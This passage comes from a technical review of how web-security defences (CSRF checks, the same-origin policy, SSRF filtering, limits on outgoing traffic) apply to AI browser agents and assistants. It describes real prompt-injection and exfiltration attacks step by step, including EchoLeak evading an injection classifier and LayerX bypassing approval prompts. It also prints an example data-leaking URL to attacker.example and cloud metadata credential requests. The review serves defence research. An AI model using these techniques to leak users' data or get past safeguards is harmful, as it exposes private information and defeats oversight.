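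Hossen therefore added a check at the service. Before the agent starts, the service receives a list of what the task authorizes, such as access for a particular application to a particular account. It refuses any other request. Agents submitted an unauthorized request in all 70 attack runs with this check, and the service refused every one. All 73 runs in which the task named the action succeeded.

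The check also works when only one detail is wrong. In one test, the task authorized access to an archive account, but the page requested access to the main account. Haiku approved the page's request in all five runs, and the service refused it each time. GPT-5.5 never submitted the request.

A CSRF token would be valid in each of these runs because it identifies the session, not the account being shared. Hossen's list includes the account, so it can stop an agent that uses the right form for the wrong purpose. But it works only if someone names the right account in advance, which the clerk doesn't do when he writes "pay the attached invoice".

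### Software that takes commands for an agent

CSRF defences still protect an agent's software against commands from a hostile web page. Such commands might start a task or change the agent's memory without the model assessing them.

*From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, 2026) describes a scenario in which an assistant saves memories through an ordinary web request. A hostile page forges that request to store a false note in the user's account, and the assistant reads the note in a later conversation. The paper does not report a real attack of this kind. A CSRF token or a `Sec-Fetch-Site` check would block the forged request, but neither would stop the assistant from saving the same note after reading it in an email.

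Some agent software runs a small server on the user's computer. A web page can make the browser send requests to this server, though the developer may assume that only local programs can reach it. Browsers include `Sec-Fetch-Site` in these requests, so the server can use the usual check. It should also check the Host header, which contains the name the browser used to reach it. Otherwise an attacker can make his own domain name point to the user's computer (DNS rebinding), and the browser will treat his page and the local server as one origin.

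AI Central's *Open Sesame!* reports that a local interface in Perplexity's Comet browser gave system-level access to the user's computer without explicit permission, until Perplexity disabled it after a disclosure in November 2025.

A WebSocket is a lasting connection through which a page and a server can exchange messages, and browsers let a page open one to another site. The opening request normally uses GET, so Valsorda's procedure would allow it at step 1. The server therefore has to check the Origin header itself before accepting the connection. If it relies only on a cookie, or accepts any local connection, a hostile page may be able to send commands to the agent and read its answers.

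Browser extensions also receive commands from web pages, and Anthropic's Claude extension for Chrome has had two flaws in how it checked the sender. *Top 6 Claude in Chrome Security Risks to Model* (Borah, 2026) describes one of them, ShadowPrompt, which researchers disclosed in March. It let any website send prompts to the extension as though the user had typed them. The extension trusted every subdomain of claude.ai, and one of them hosted a third-party component with a cross-site scripting (XSS) flaw. An exact list of trusted origins, as Valsorda recommends, could have excluded that subdomain.

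The security company LayerX reported the second flaw, ClaudeBleed, to Anthropic in April 2026, and it became public in May. The extension accepted messages from claude.ai without checking which program had sent them. Another extension, even one with no special permissions, could run a script inside the claude.ai page and send commands from there. LayerX used this to make Claude share a private file with an outsider and send email in the user's name.

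An exact origin check doesn't help against ClaudeBleed because the messages came from claude.ai. A secret token in the page would probably have failed too, since a script running in the page could read it. LayerX recommended signed messages, a list of trusted extensions instead of trusted websites, and approvals that each apply to one action. Signing would help only if other scripts in the page could neither read the key nor get the page to sign their messages.

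Anthropic's 6 May update added approval prompts. LayerX bypassed them by using a mode in which Claude acts without asking, and argued that the extension still did not verify the sender. Borah wrote in September that Anthropic had closed both flaws.

### Signing the instructions

A website can recognise its own forms by a token, and an agent's program might recognise the user's instructions in a similar way. *A2AS* (2025), a proposed security framework for agents, puts each user prompt between tags that contain a hash, a short value computed from the prompt's content, origin and other details. The program checks the hash before the model reads the prompt, and can reject the prompt if the hash is wrong. *Prompt Fencing* (2025) applies cryptographic signatures to parts of a prompt.

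Such a check can detect a prompt that an attacker has altered or sent in the user's name, if the attacker can't produce a valid hash or signature. It might have detected ShadowPrompt's forged prompts if the extension had signed only what the user typed in its own window.

The false Halvorsen email doesn't have to imitate the clerk's prompt, because the assistant fetches it as part of its work. The program can't reject all unsigned text, because the assistant would then be unable to read mail, so the model receives the clerk's signed request and the unsigned email together. The program can verify the signature with near certainty, but it can't make the model follow only the signed text, and the same is true of the other markers in a model's input.

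*Prompt Injection Attacks on Agentic Coding Assistants* (2026) makes a related point about signed tool definitions. A signature can show who published a file-deletion tool, but an attacker may still get the agent to use it to delete the wrong file.

Signed permissions are more useful if a program checks them before each action. *Large Language Models for Cyber Security* (2025) describes a scheme called Encrypted Prompt, which attaches the user's current permissions to their prompt and uses a pair of cryptographic keys to protect them against changes. Like an on-behalf-of token, this scheme would stop the sales employee's request for salaries but not the clerk's payment to the fraudster.

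*Protecting Context and Prompts* (2026) describes a system that tracks an instruction through several steps by signing each prompt and linking it to the user's original one. For example, a request to analyse quarterly sales might lead an agent to write a further prompt asking for the revenue in a particular report. A derived prompt like this can add restrictions but can't remove any, and the system limits how many times an agent can derive one prompt from another.

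Attenuation, as used in macaroons, can be applied to prompts by requiring that a derived prompt only narrow the original. If a clerk's prompt allows only reading, an email cannot make the assistant send a payment. But if he asks the assistant to pay Halvorsen without giving an account number, a derived prompt with a fraudster's account number may be accepted, because specifying an account narrows the original instruction.

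## The same-origin policy in browsers driven by agents

CSRF defences control which pages can send requests in a user's name. Another browser rule, the same-origin policy, controls which pages can read the responses. It stops a script on a fraudster's page from reading the clerk's balance or the secret token in the bank's payment form.

### What the policy leaves to people

A page's origin consists of the scheme, host and port in its address, so two pages on the same host have different origins if one uses http and the other https. The browser labels each page's scripts and data with that origin and blocks scripts from one origin from reading another origin's data.

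People often move data between sites, and the policy does not restrict them. The clerk can copy an account number from his webmail and paste it into the bank's form. *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) counts this as an authorized transfer because a person decided on it and carried it out. The policy exists to stop scripts from making such transfers automatically.

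A browser agent works automatically, as a script does, but it moves data between sites the way a person does. It can read a webmail page, keep the text in the model's context, and later type some of it into a form on another site. The same-origin policy doesn't block this, because no script on either page has read the other page. An attacker who can write on the second page can therefore plant an instruction there that gets the agent to type in what it read on the first, which a script on the second page could not have read.

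### What seven browsers let their agents see

In *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026) tested seven browsers with built-in or added agents in January and February 2026. They spread simple facts, such as which animals someone called Alice likes, across several tabs and iframes, and asked each agent about them. An iframe is a page embedded in another page, as many advertisements are. If the two pages have different origins, the same-origin policy stops them from reading each other's contents.

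| Agent | Reads an iframe from another origin | Reads a tab from another origin | Types into pages when the user asks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Brave Leo AI | No | With permission | No |
| ChatGPT Atlas | No | Only through chat memory | After permission to enter Agent Mode |
| ChatGPT Atlas, Agent Mode | Yes | No | Yes |
| Chrome with Gemini | Yes | With permission | Yes, in Auto Browse |
| Claude for Chrome | Yes | With permission | Yes |
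| Edge with Copilot | No | Yes | No |
| Firefox AI Mode | No | No | No |
| Perplexity Comet | Yes | No | Yes, except passwords |

The agents that could not read an iframe from another origin could not read one from the same origin either, which is stricter than the policy requires. Firefox's agent is the most cautious. It receives a page's text only when the user clicks a button to summarize the page, and the text leaves out embedded iframes. Copilot does not read iframes either, but it reads every open tab without asking the user.

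Two agents had further powers that would help an attacker. Atlas in Agent Mode and Claude for Chrome read passwords that the page displayed as dots. Claude for Chrome, an extension with access to all sites, could also run its own JavaScript inside a page, including in an iframe from another origin.

An attacker can exploit this access with a page that embeds a private page from another site. The attacker's page contains instructions for the agent to include the embedded page in any summary and enter that summary in a form, which submits itself. The user only has to open the page and ask for a summary. This attack worked against Atlas in Agent Mode. The reverse also worked, with a hostile iframe taking data from the page around it. The reverse attack is more worrying because most sites with private data now restrict embedding, whereas pages with private data may well carry advertisements.

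Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Comet gave their agents enough access for the same attack, but the models refused to follow the planted text. Roesner and Kohlbrenner had not tried to write a sophisticated injection. In their basic test, the user told the agent to do what the page instructed, so following the planted text was less clearly a failure. OpenAI declined their report because it did not contain a complete injection attack. The study is therefore better evidence of what the agents could reach than of how often an attack would succeed. But when an agent can reach everything, the separation between sites depends on the model's resistance to injection.

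An agent's memory can carry false information from one site into later answers, even without prompt injection. Atlas, Gemini and Comet drew on earlier chats when they answered questions about a new page. Suppose a user asks for a summary of a site that impersonates his bank and gives a false telephone number. If he asks for the bank's number weeks later, the agent may repeat the false one without recalling which site it came from. The researchers did not try this attack, but Comet did combine information about Alice's animals from pages they had visited earlier. Their paper advises people to avoid agentic browsers for now. Roesner and Kohlbrenner's web page for the general public advises only caution, and warns most strongly about Claude for Chrome because it can run scripts.

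### How often data crosses

Wang and colleagues measured such leaks with a benchmark called SOPBench. In a typical run, the user first has the agent carry out a task on a page with private data, such as a bank account or a pharmacy order. The user then opens another page, such as a Reddit thread, and asks the agent to post an ordinary comment. An attacker has planted a message in the thread instructing the agent to write the private data there. The benchmark pairs ten types of private page with five types of receiving page, for 50 combinations. Wang and colleagues had GPT-5.4 generate most of the pages, so no real data was at risk. They counted a violation only if the agent wrote exactly the data that the attacker wanted.

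The tests covered five browsers, which used six models between them. With GPT-5.4, the open-source browser BrowserOS leaked data to Reddit in 3–42% of runs, depending on the type of private page. On Google Forms, where the attacker can own the whole page and the agent is already filling in fields, it leaked data in 81–100% of runs. The planted text in these runs was written by hand. When a language model rewrote the text after each failed attack, the Reddit figures rose to 31–73%.

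The commercial browsers did no better. Atlas with GPT-5.5 leaked data in 99 of 150 runs. Comet did so in 92 of 150 with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and in 100 of 150 with Gemini 3.1 Pro. Each combination has only three runs because somebody had to operate these browsers by hand. The models are also older than those with the lowest attack success rates today, and newer ones would probably leak less.

SOPBench also includes violations without an attacker, which Wang and colleagues call passive. The receiving page embeds a private page from another origin, and the user asks the agent to summarize the whole page and write the summary into a text box on it. BrowserOS copied the private data in every run with all three models tested.

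This perfect score needs some discounting because the user asked for the whole page, which makes it debatable whether the transfer was unauthorized, and because few private pages allow other sites to embed them. Wang and colleagues saw no leaks when the agent visited the private page and the receiving page one after the other, with nothing planted on either.

### Asking before data crosses

Wang and colleagues built a defence, SOPGuard, into BrowserOS. It applies the same-origin policy to what the agent writes:

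1. **Labelling.** When the agent reads a page, SOPGuard stores the text together with the page's origin.
2. **Propagation.** When the model produces something new, such as the total of three invoices, SOPGuard asks the model which stored texts it used. The new text receives all their origins.
3. **Detection.** Before the agent types a text $x$ into a page $w$, SOPGuard compares the text's origins, $O_x$, with the page's own origin, $o(w)$. It interrupts the agent if any origin in $O_x$ differs from $o(w)$.
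4. **Confirmation.** A window names the origins involved, and the user approves or refuses the transfer.

SOPGuard's second step, asking the model which origins its text came from, is unusual. FIDES instead gives everything a model writes the combined label of its whole context. Under that rule, SOPGuard would interrupt almost every entry the agent made after its first change of site, including text that came entirely from the page it was working on. Asking the model is more precise. With GPT-5.4 and o3, the origins the model named overlapped with the correct ones by at least 95.5% on average, even when the agent had read pages from ten origins.

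The drawback of this precision is that a security check depends on a model that reads the attacker's text. Wang and colleagues tried to exploit this with planted text that also told the model to name the current page as its only source. The attack raised the violation rate only slightly, because the same text has to make the model both misuse the data and misreport its source, and SOPGuard often doesn't need to query the model because the private data matches a stored text exactly. They acknowledge that a better attack may exist. Some mistakes are also harmless. For example, if the model omits one of two foreign origins, the other still triggers the window.

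Except under these tailored attacks, SOPGuard reduced violations on SOPBench to zero. Tasks took 2.07–5.79% longer, and Wang and colleagues found no significant change in how many the agent completed. A violation here is a transfer the user has not approved, so the result doesn't show how well people judge the requests.

Five alternative programs that look for injected text did much worse. WebSentinel, for example, missed at most 1% of the hostile pages but flagged 6–44% of harmless ones, depending on the site. No such program can catch a passive violation, because it involves no injected text.

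If the clerk uses SOPGuard to pay invoices from his webmail, the window appears every time the agent copies an account number into the bank's form. It correctly names the mail site and the bank whether the invoice is genuine or forged. It doesn't show whose account it is, so the clerk learns only that data is about to move between the two sites, which he already knew.

### Choosing the sites for each task

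Google's approach is to decide in advance which sites the agent needs. Parker (2025), in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, describes it as extending the browser's existing separation between sites. Google launched the agent, called auto browse, in January 2026, according to Bloomberg's *Google Chrome’s AI Agent Can Now Browse Web on Behalf of Users* (2026).

For each task, Chrome keeps Agent Origin Sets, two lists of origins. The agent may read pages from origins on the first list, and may also click and type on pages from origins on the second. If the user wants the ingredients of a recipe in his shopping basket, the recipe site belongs on the first list and the shop on the second. The browser does not pass the model anything from an origin on neither list, so an advertisement embedded in the recipe page never reaches the model. Private data can leak only from a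 listed site to a site where the agent may write.

The planning model reads web pages, so an attacker could get it to request access to more sites. For this reason, the model can only propose an origin, and a separate gating function that receives no untrusted web content decides whether the origin is relevant to the task. Chrome also restricts the addresses the model writes to known public ones, because the model could otherwise hide private data in an address.

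Another model, the User Alignment Critic, reviews each action before it happens. It receives the user's goal and a description of the proposed action, but not the page, so text on the page can't reach it directly. If an action doesn't serve the goal, the critic vetoes it and sends the planner the reason. After repeated failures, the planner can return control to the user. The critic borrows from the dual-model pattern, but unlike in that pattern, Chrome's planner reads untrusted pages.

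Parker writes that the first version kept only the list of origins where the agent could both read and write. Roesner and Kohlbrenner found in tests a few weeks later that Gemini still read iframes from other origins, as one would expect if the list of readable origins was not yet in use. They also note that Google has not explained how Chrome judges relevance or how well that judgment resists malicious input.

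Even the full design lets the agent move data between sites whenever the task needs it. Paying an invoice requires both the webmail and the bank. A critic without access to the email or the supplier records would classify the payment as serving the clerk's goal, and could not detect that the account belongs to the fraudster. Chrome's remaining protection is user confirmation, which it requires before the agent opens a banking site. It also tries to pause again before any payment.

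### Neither sufficient nor necessary

Zverev and colleagues argue that restoring the same-origin policy for agents is the wrong aim because it is neither sufficient nor necessary to protect users. They support each claim with a case from their tests.

In the first attack, a direct message on a social network tells the agent to copy the user's private recovery address into his public profile. The address and the profile are on the same site, so no data moves between origins. SOPGuard raised no alarm, and the attack succeeded in all 25 runs.

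In the second case, the user wants to know whether a discount on a speaker is real. The agent has to copy the product's name from a deals site into a shopping search engine. None of this is private or dangerous, but SOPGuard interrupted the agent in all 25 runs, with 33 requests for approval in total. The same-origin policy never stopped a person from making this comparison, so this case counts only against applying the policy to agents.

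SPIDES labels the parts of a page separately. A shop's page may contain a product name written by the shop, a review written by a stranger and the last digits of the user's card, all from one origin. The shop's developers mark the review as untrusted and list the user and the shop as the only parties who may read the card details. Elements inside a marked element inherit its labels unless they have their own.

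The user keeps a list of sites whose operators he trusts to do this, and SPIDES assumes that he has accounts only on those sites. It treats everything on other sites as untrusted and public. As in FIDES, the agent sees variable names in place of untrusted or private text, and when it opens a variable, its context takes on that variable's label.

SPIDES then has to judge clicks and keystrokes, which is harder than judging a call to `pay_invoice`. A click might open a menu or delete an account, and the browser can't know which until it happens. The rules therefore assume the worst that an action could do at its target:

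| Agent's action | Condition |
|---|---|
| Reading a page or switching tabs | None |
| Clicking, navigating or submitting on a listed site | Nothing untrusted has influenced the action |
| The same actions on any other site | Nothing untrusted has influenced the action, or the site may receive the data |
| Typing without submitting, on any site | Nothing untrusted has influenced the action, or the site may receive the data |
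| Running code in a page | Always refused |

If an action other than running code fails its condition, SPIDES asks the user. The stricter rule applies to trusted sites because those are the sites where the user has accounts, and so the only ones where a click can spend his money or change his settings.

A site with origin $o$ may receive the data if

$$o \in R_{\mathrm{ctx}} \cap R_{\mathrm{arg}}$$

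where $R_{\mathrm{ctx}}$ is the set of readers allowed to see everything the agent has opened, and $R_{\mathrm{arg}}$ is the same for any hidden values in the text it is about to send. In the attack on the public profile, this condition allows the agent to type the recovery address, since the social network already has it. But the hostile message has made the agent's context untrusted by then, so SPIDES does not let it click "Save changes". SPIDES blocked all 25 runs. For the speaker, it asked for no approval in 21 of 25 runs and made nine requests in the other four.

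### Two benchmarks, two verdicts on SOPGuard

Zverev and colleagues compared the systems on MicroNet, a closed set of 28 linked websites that they built and labelled. MicroNet has 56 ordinary tasks, 22 of which require moving data between sites, and 56 attacks.

The researchers assumed that the model would obey any planted instruction. As soon as one reached the model, the test program replaced the model's answer with the tool calls that the attacker would want, so good training could make no difference and only the checks outside the model could stop the attack. Six of the attacks used false data instead of instructions. For these, the researchers let the model answer for itself because they could not script every possible answer beforehand.

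The table shows the share of tasks completed when there was no attack and the share of attacks that succeeded. SPIDES is missing from the last two columns because no attack succeeded against it with any model.

| Model | Tasks, no defence | Tasks, SOPGuard | Tasks, SPIDES | Attacks, no defence | Attacks, SOPGuard |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 91.1% | 93.2% | 86.1% | 95.7% | 57.9% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 88.2% | 85.7% | 77.1% | 95.0% | 58.2% |
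| Claude Opus 5.5 | 58.2% | 58.2% | 67.1% | 57.5% | 53.2% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 68.9% | 66.1% | 69.3% | 71.8% | 65.7% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 88.9% | 90.0% | 82.1% | 92.5% | 73.2% |

With Opus 5.5, the agent completed more tasks under SPIDES than without any defence. Some tasks included passwords or phishing messages, and the provider's safety classifiers stopped the model when it saw them. SPIDES avoided some of these refusals by hiding this material from the main model.

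SOPGuard has a perfect score on SOPBench because every violation there carries data from one site to another, which is what SOPGuard checks for. On MicroNet, 26 of the 56 attacks stay within one site, and half of the 56 aim at an unauthorized action that doesn't require leaking private data. SOPGuard has no rule against either. The substituted answers also remove any protection the model's own caution might have added. Both results are correct, but SOPBench measures whether SOPGuard enforces the same-origin policy, while MicroNet measures whether the user is harmed.

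MicroNet favours SPIDES because the same researchers made both, and every page carries the accurate labels that SPIDES needs. Zverev and colleagues did not run SPIDES on SOPBench, but it would probably do badly on the passive violations, because SPIDES allows the agent to send private data anywhere as long as nothing untrusted has influenced the decision. If an agent carelessly put bank details in a public comment, with no attacker involved, SPIDES would allow it, whereas SOPGuard would ask first.

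The six attacks with false data matter most for invoices. An earlier system, UCM, hides untrusted text from the main model but lets a second model pass on short answers, such as a number or a choice from a list. It stopped every planted instruction, but the attacks with false data succeeded in 43–63% of runs, depending on the model. SPIDES stopped these attacks because once the agent opens a hidden value, the context becomes untrusted and any consequential click needs approval. If the agent opens the email to find Halvorsen's account number, the clerk has to approve the payment, whether or not the invoice is genuine.

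SPIDES requested 1.84 user approvals per completed task, compared with 0.22 for SOPGuard. Zverev and colleagues simulated a user who always distinguishes safe requests from unsafe ones, so the zero in their results depends on perfect judgment. When they tightened the other systems to give the same guarantees, SPIDES generally completed the most tasks for a small number of requests.

### Who labels the web

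SPIDES depends on site operators to label their pages, and its defaults make this risky. On a site that the user has listed, it treats any unlabelled element as trusted and public. If the operator of a listed shop has labelled nothing, a stranger's review counts as the shop's own text, and the user's address counts as public. If the user leaves the shop off the list, SPIDES ignores the danger to the user's account there. Zverev and colleagues compare labelling to providing accessibility information, which many sites already do, but a missing accessibility label doesn't let anyone steal money.

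The lists of readers also contain only whole sites. A list can allow a message to go to the company's chat service, but it can't limit the message to the clerk's manager and exclude an outsider who has an account there.

ceLLMate, by Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025), in *CELLMATE*, relies on operators in another way. It ignores what is on the page and checks the HTTP requests that the browser sends. A click at certain coordinates means nothing by itself, but the request that follows it does, for instance when it adds an access key to an account. Operators publish an agent sitemap that gives each such request a name, such as "PlaceOrder". They or another trusted party write rules that use these names, such as a limit on the price of an order. A language model picks the rules that fit the user's task before the agent opens any page, and the user confirms them.

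To test this, Meng and colleagues assumed that the attacker had full control of the agent, and wrote 12 scripts that attacked the programming site GitLab directly. The user's task needed only permission to read and write issues, and ceLLMate blocked all 12 attacks. Pages took 7.25–15% longer to load. The models chose the right rules for at least 94% of tasks, though they sometimes granted more access than the task needed.

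ceLLMate would also stop SPIDES's example of the public profile, unless the user's task involved editing it. But it does not track where data came from, so an attacker can still misuse whatever the rules allow. An agent with permission to comment on an issue can put a secret in the comment. Paying invoices has the same weakness unless the rules also fix the payee.

Villa, Tan and colleagues (2026), in *Prismata*, try to do without the operators' help by having language models work out the labels from the page's structure. The difficulty is that a model which reads the page to label it also reads the attacker's text. Prismata limits this exposure with two checks:

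- **Each button or field by itself.** A model sees the user's task, the button and the chain of page elements that enclose it, and decides whether the task needs the button. A hostile review elsewhere on the page is not part of this input.
- **The page from the outside in.** A model labels each layer before it sees the next. If it meets a heading such as "Reviews", it marks everything below as outsiders' text without reading it. Nothing inside can gain more trust than its surroundings.

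Because the stricter result applies, an attacker must place text among the elements that enclose a useful button, with no heading or similar warning sign before it. Villa and colleagues searched 5,664 real pages for such places. Of 90,408 paths to outsiders' content, 1.2% led to something an agent could click or fill in, and only 94, about 0.1%, did so without a warning sign. Language models did much of the annotation for this count, so the count includes some of the same labelling errors it is meant to assess.

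In tests with three kinds of hostile pop-up, Prismata reduced the average attack success rate from 85.5% to 0.7%. When there was no attack, the agent completed 26.6% of its tasks with Prismata and 29.9% without it. The agent used GPT-5.4-mini and was already weak, so it is hard to judge how much Prismata would reduce a better agent's performance. Prismata covers only text, so an agent that works from screenshots could still read an instruction in an image.

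Villa and colleagues exclude attacks that stay within what the task requires, such as a fake review that sways a purchase when the user has asked for the best-reviewed product. The forged Halvorsen invoice is another such attack, because the agent has to read the email and press the bank's payment button. Prismata would therefore have to leave both available.

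## Defences against server-side request forgery and limits on outgoing traffic

The office assistant's `fetch_url` tool runs inside the company network, so it can open pages that outsiders cannot. Many web applications also fetch addresses for their users, and outsiders exploit this in an attack called server-side request forgery (SSRF). MDN's *Server Side Request Forgery (SSRF)* describes a site that fetches an image from any address a user supplies. If the site doesn't check the address, a user can enter the address of an intranet page and read the reply.

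The site is a confused deputy because the user designates the page, but the authority to read it comes from the server's place in the network. Internal services often grant that authority without requiring a password. OWASP's *Top Ten Proactive Controls 2024* (2024) notes that many servers run local services with no login.

CSRF defences check where a request came from, whereas SSRF defences check where it is going.

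### Checking the address

The safest check is a list of permitted hosts. *Server-Side Request Forgery (SSRF)* reproduces OWASP's advice to specify the permitted scheme, port and destination in such a list and to turn off redirects. OWASP also warns against relying on lists of forbidden addresses, because attackers have ready-made collections of bypasses.

A tool for reading the open web can't work from a short list of hosts. Its developer can instead block the address ranges reserved for private networks and for the machine itself. This is still a list of forbidden addresses, but it covers numerical ranges, so a different spelling of the URL makes no difference. For each request, the tool goes through these steps:

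1. Refuse any scheme other than http or https.
2. If there is a list of permitted hosts, refuse a host that does not exactly match an entry.
3. Look up the host's numerical address, and refuse it if it lies in a private or local range.
4. Connect to that same address without looking it up again.
5. If the reply is a redirect, start again at step 1 with the new URL.

Step 3 comes after the lookup because an attacker can point a harmless-looking domain to an internal machine. Step 4 prevents DNS rebinding, in which the attacker's domain resolves to a public address when the tool checks it and a private one when the tool connects.

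The exact match in step 2 also matters. Vulners' *Claude Code has a Domain Validation Bypass* describes a flaw in Anthropic's coding agent, which compared only the beginning of an address with trusted names such as `docs.python.org`. The host `docs.python.org.attacker.example` would pass such a check.

None of these steps involves interpreting a sentence. If an email tells the office assistant to open the internal payroll page, the model may well write the call, but the tool blocks it. The tool also blocks the call if the sales employee asks for the page himself, so one check covers both the content case and the caller case.

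The tool's code has to check addresses, because models do so unreliably. Mindgard's *TheLibrarian.io Internal Cloud Environment Access via web_fetch Tool* (2025) describes an AI assistant that refused to fetch `http://localhost` but accepted encoded or less obvious forms of internal addresses. For instance, a model may not recognise `http://2130706433` as the local machine, but a program that converts it to a standard IP address gets 127.0.0.1.

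Staff may want the assistant to read some internal pages, and an address check doesn't establish which employees may see them. To read those pages, the tool needs to use the requesting employee's permissions, for example through an on-behalf-of token. An agent that runs its own code can send requests without `fetch_url`, so the company has to enforce the limits on all traffic leaving the agent's machine.

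Some requests don't involve the model. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP, points out that while setting up a login, a client fetches several addresses supplied by a server. A malicious server can supply an internal address, so the client needs the same check.

### A metadata service that requires a token

On a cloud machine, the most valuable internal address is often 169.254.169.254. The provider runs a metadata service there, which gives programs on the machine temporary credentials for the machine's role. In the first version of Amazon's service, a program could get these credentials with a plain GET request, which almost any SSRF flaw allows an outsider to send.

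Security Horror's *OLD BUG, NEW DELIVERY* (2026) calls the breach at the American bank Capital One the canonical example of server-side request forgery. In 2019 an attacker sent requests through a misconfigured firewall, obtained the credentials of the firewall's role, and copied data on about 100 million people in the United States and six million in Canada. The role could read stored customer data, which a firewall does not need to do.

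Amazon released a second version, IMDSv2, later that year. A program now has to make two requests:

```text
PUT /latest/api/token
X-aws-ec2-metadata-token-ttl-seconds: 60

GET /latest/meta-data/iam/security-credentials/
X-aws-ec2-metadata-token: (token from the first reply)
```

The service refuses the second request unless it includes the session token from the first. A flawed image fetcher that sends only GET requests with fixed headers can't make either request. The service also rejects token requests that carry a header commonly added by proxies. These checks help only if the machine's owner has switched off the first version of the service.

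IMDSv2 protects `fetch_url` in the same way, as long as the model supplies only an address. If an agent has a shell, or a more general tool that takes the method and headers as arguments, an attacker can describe both the token request and the metadata request in an email, and the model can send them. The developer then has to block the metadata address or give the machine a role with no permissions worth stealing.

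### How many MCP servers have the flaw

Many MCP servers lack these checks, though estimates of how many differ widely. *A Measurement Study of Model Context Protocol Ecosystem* (2025) found code that makes network requests in more than 2,700 servers, but such code is harmless if it checks the address. Security Horror reports that the security company BlueRock scanned over 7,000 public servers early in 2026 and found 36.7% "potentially vulnerable". CloudSEK repeats the figure without the word "potentially". *MCP-38* cites an industry estimate of up to 30%.

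Researchers who tried the attack found the flaw less often. *Exposed by Design* (Padilla, 2026) audited 414 public MCP servers in July 2026 and recorded SSRF on 29 (7%). In April, CyberneticsPlus (2026) reported testing 100 servers and confirming 15 flaws, seven of them SSRF. Trend Micro's *Hunt Them All* found that only 4.1% of the flaws an AI had identified in servers' code were exploitable. It estimated that 3.1–8.6% of some 19,000 code repositories contained an exploitable flaw of any kind. The samples differ, but the share of servers with an exploitable SSRF flaw is probably well below BlueRock's figure.

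Even Padilla's count is an estimate, because the test often relied on timing. For example, a document server called epwforge took 11.9 seconds to respond when asked to fetch the metadata address, but 0.3 seconds for an address that leads nowhere. Padilla concluded that the server could reach the metadata service and, by implication, its credentials. But a metadata service normally answers almost at once, so the delay could also have been a connection timing out. The remedy for epwforge was a list of permitted domains, as it would be for a web application.

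### When the address carries the data

In classical SSRF the attacker wants something at the destination. An agent has often read private data already, and an ordinary request to a public site is then enough to leak it. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives an example like this:

```text
https://attacker.example/collect?data=<something private>
```

Web servers commonly log the URLs that visitors request, so the attacker can read the data in his log. A check that blocks private IP addresses allows the request because attacker.example is a public site.

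An agent can leak data without using a tool. If its answer includes an image whose address contains the data, the user's browser sends the data to the image's host by fetching the image as soon as it displays the answer. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* says that its author reported this leak to OpenAI and Microsoft in 2023. Microsoft fixed it in Bing Chat that May with a content security policy, a header that can limit the hosts from which a page loads images. OpenAI added its first check in December.

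### EchoLeak and SearchLeak

In January 2025 the research group Aim Labs found a way past such a policy in Microsoft 365 Copilot, which answers employees' questions from their mail and files. The attack, EchoLeak, needed one email and no click. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, describes how it worked:

1. The attacker emailed an employee. The text addressed the human reader and never mentioned an AI, which got it past Microsoft's injection classifier.
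2. The email repeated its instructions under headings such as employee onboarding and leave of absence. Copilot was therefore likely to retrieve it when the employee asked about any of these topics.
3. The instructions were to take the most sensitive information available and put it in an image's address.
4. Copilot normally removed external links from its answers, but it missed a notation that puts the address on a separate line.
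5. The employee's browser fetched the image from a Microsoft Teams address, which the content security policy permitted.
6. That address contained another one, on the attacker's server. Teams fetched it, and the private data appeared in the attacker's log.

*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) classifies the last step as SSRF because a Microsoft server fetched an address that an outsider had chosen. Ravia compares the whole attack to the misuse of a Unix program that runs with its owner's permissions, because an outsider's email used Copilot's access to reach the victim's data. Microsoft fixed the flaw in May 2025, before Aim Labs published it, and reported that no customers had been affected.

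The policy Ravia published also permitted images from any host under bing.com. In June 2026, Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) disclosed an attack that sent data out through Bing. The victim clicked a link to Microsoft's own site, and the link contained instructions that Copilot carried out as a search. Copilot looked up an email and wrote an image tag whose address included the email's title.

Copilot turned the tag into harmless text only after the answer was complete, but the browser loaded the image while the answer was still appearing. The request went to Bing's search-by-image feature, which fetched the supposed image from the attacker's server. An email's subject line can contain a security code, so this leak could help an attacker break into an account. Microsoft has fixed this flaw too.

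Varonis advises companies to treat any permitted host that fetches user-supplied addresses as a possible way for data to leave. That makes a list of permitted hosts much harder to review, because someone has to examine every feature of every listed service and repeat the work when a service adds one.

### Whose account receives the data

An attacker with an account on a permitted host can receive stolen data there, even if the host doesn't forward anything. Anthropic's Claude Cowork, an agent that works with a user's files, by default allows outgoing web requests only to certain domains, including the one for Anthropic's own API. In January, Willison (2026) described an attack on it by the security company PromptArmor. The agent followed planted instructions to upload the user's files with the attacker's API key, which the instructions supplied. The upload wasn't blocked because it went to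 a permitted host, and the files ended up in the attacker's account.

A filter that checks only host names treats an upload to the user's account the same as one to the attacker's account on the same service, because the host name identifies the service and only the key identifies the account. SharePoint, Microsoft's document service, includes the customer's name in the host name, but Copilot's policy permitted every host under sharepoint.com. Ravia's team built another version of EchoLeak that used the attacker's own SharePoint site, although the victim first had to accept an invitation to the site.

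A gateway outside the agent could attach the user's key to each request and remove any other key. The upload would then go to the user's own account. This helps less with services meant to send things to other people. For example, the office assistant has to reach the bank, and a one-cent payment to an attacker could carry a password in its description field. Vissers and Van hamme used that field to get instructions into Bunq's assistant. To prevent such a leak, the company has to check the payee or keep confidentiality labels on the text.

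Some leaks don't need an account on the host. Trail of Bits got a browser agent to open an address such as `leaked-data.wikipedia.org`, which does not exist. The computer still tries to look up the name, and anyone who can watch its unencrypted lookups can read the data. In another test, the agent searched Google for private data together with rare words. An attacker who owns a site can watch for those words in Google's tool that shows site owners which searches lead to their pages.

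Trail of Bits proposes a strict limit on web requests. If an agent has read content from one site, it may send requests only to that site, and if it has read from several, it may send none. This would block both leaks, since the attacker's text and the private data come from different places. It would also stop a browser agent from reading an invoice in the clerk's webmail and paying it at the bank.

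### Opening only addresses that have appeared before

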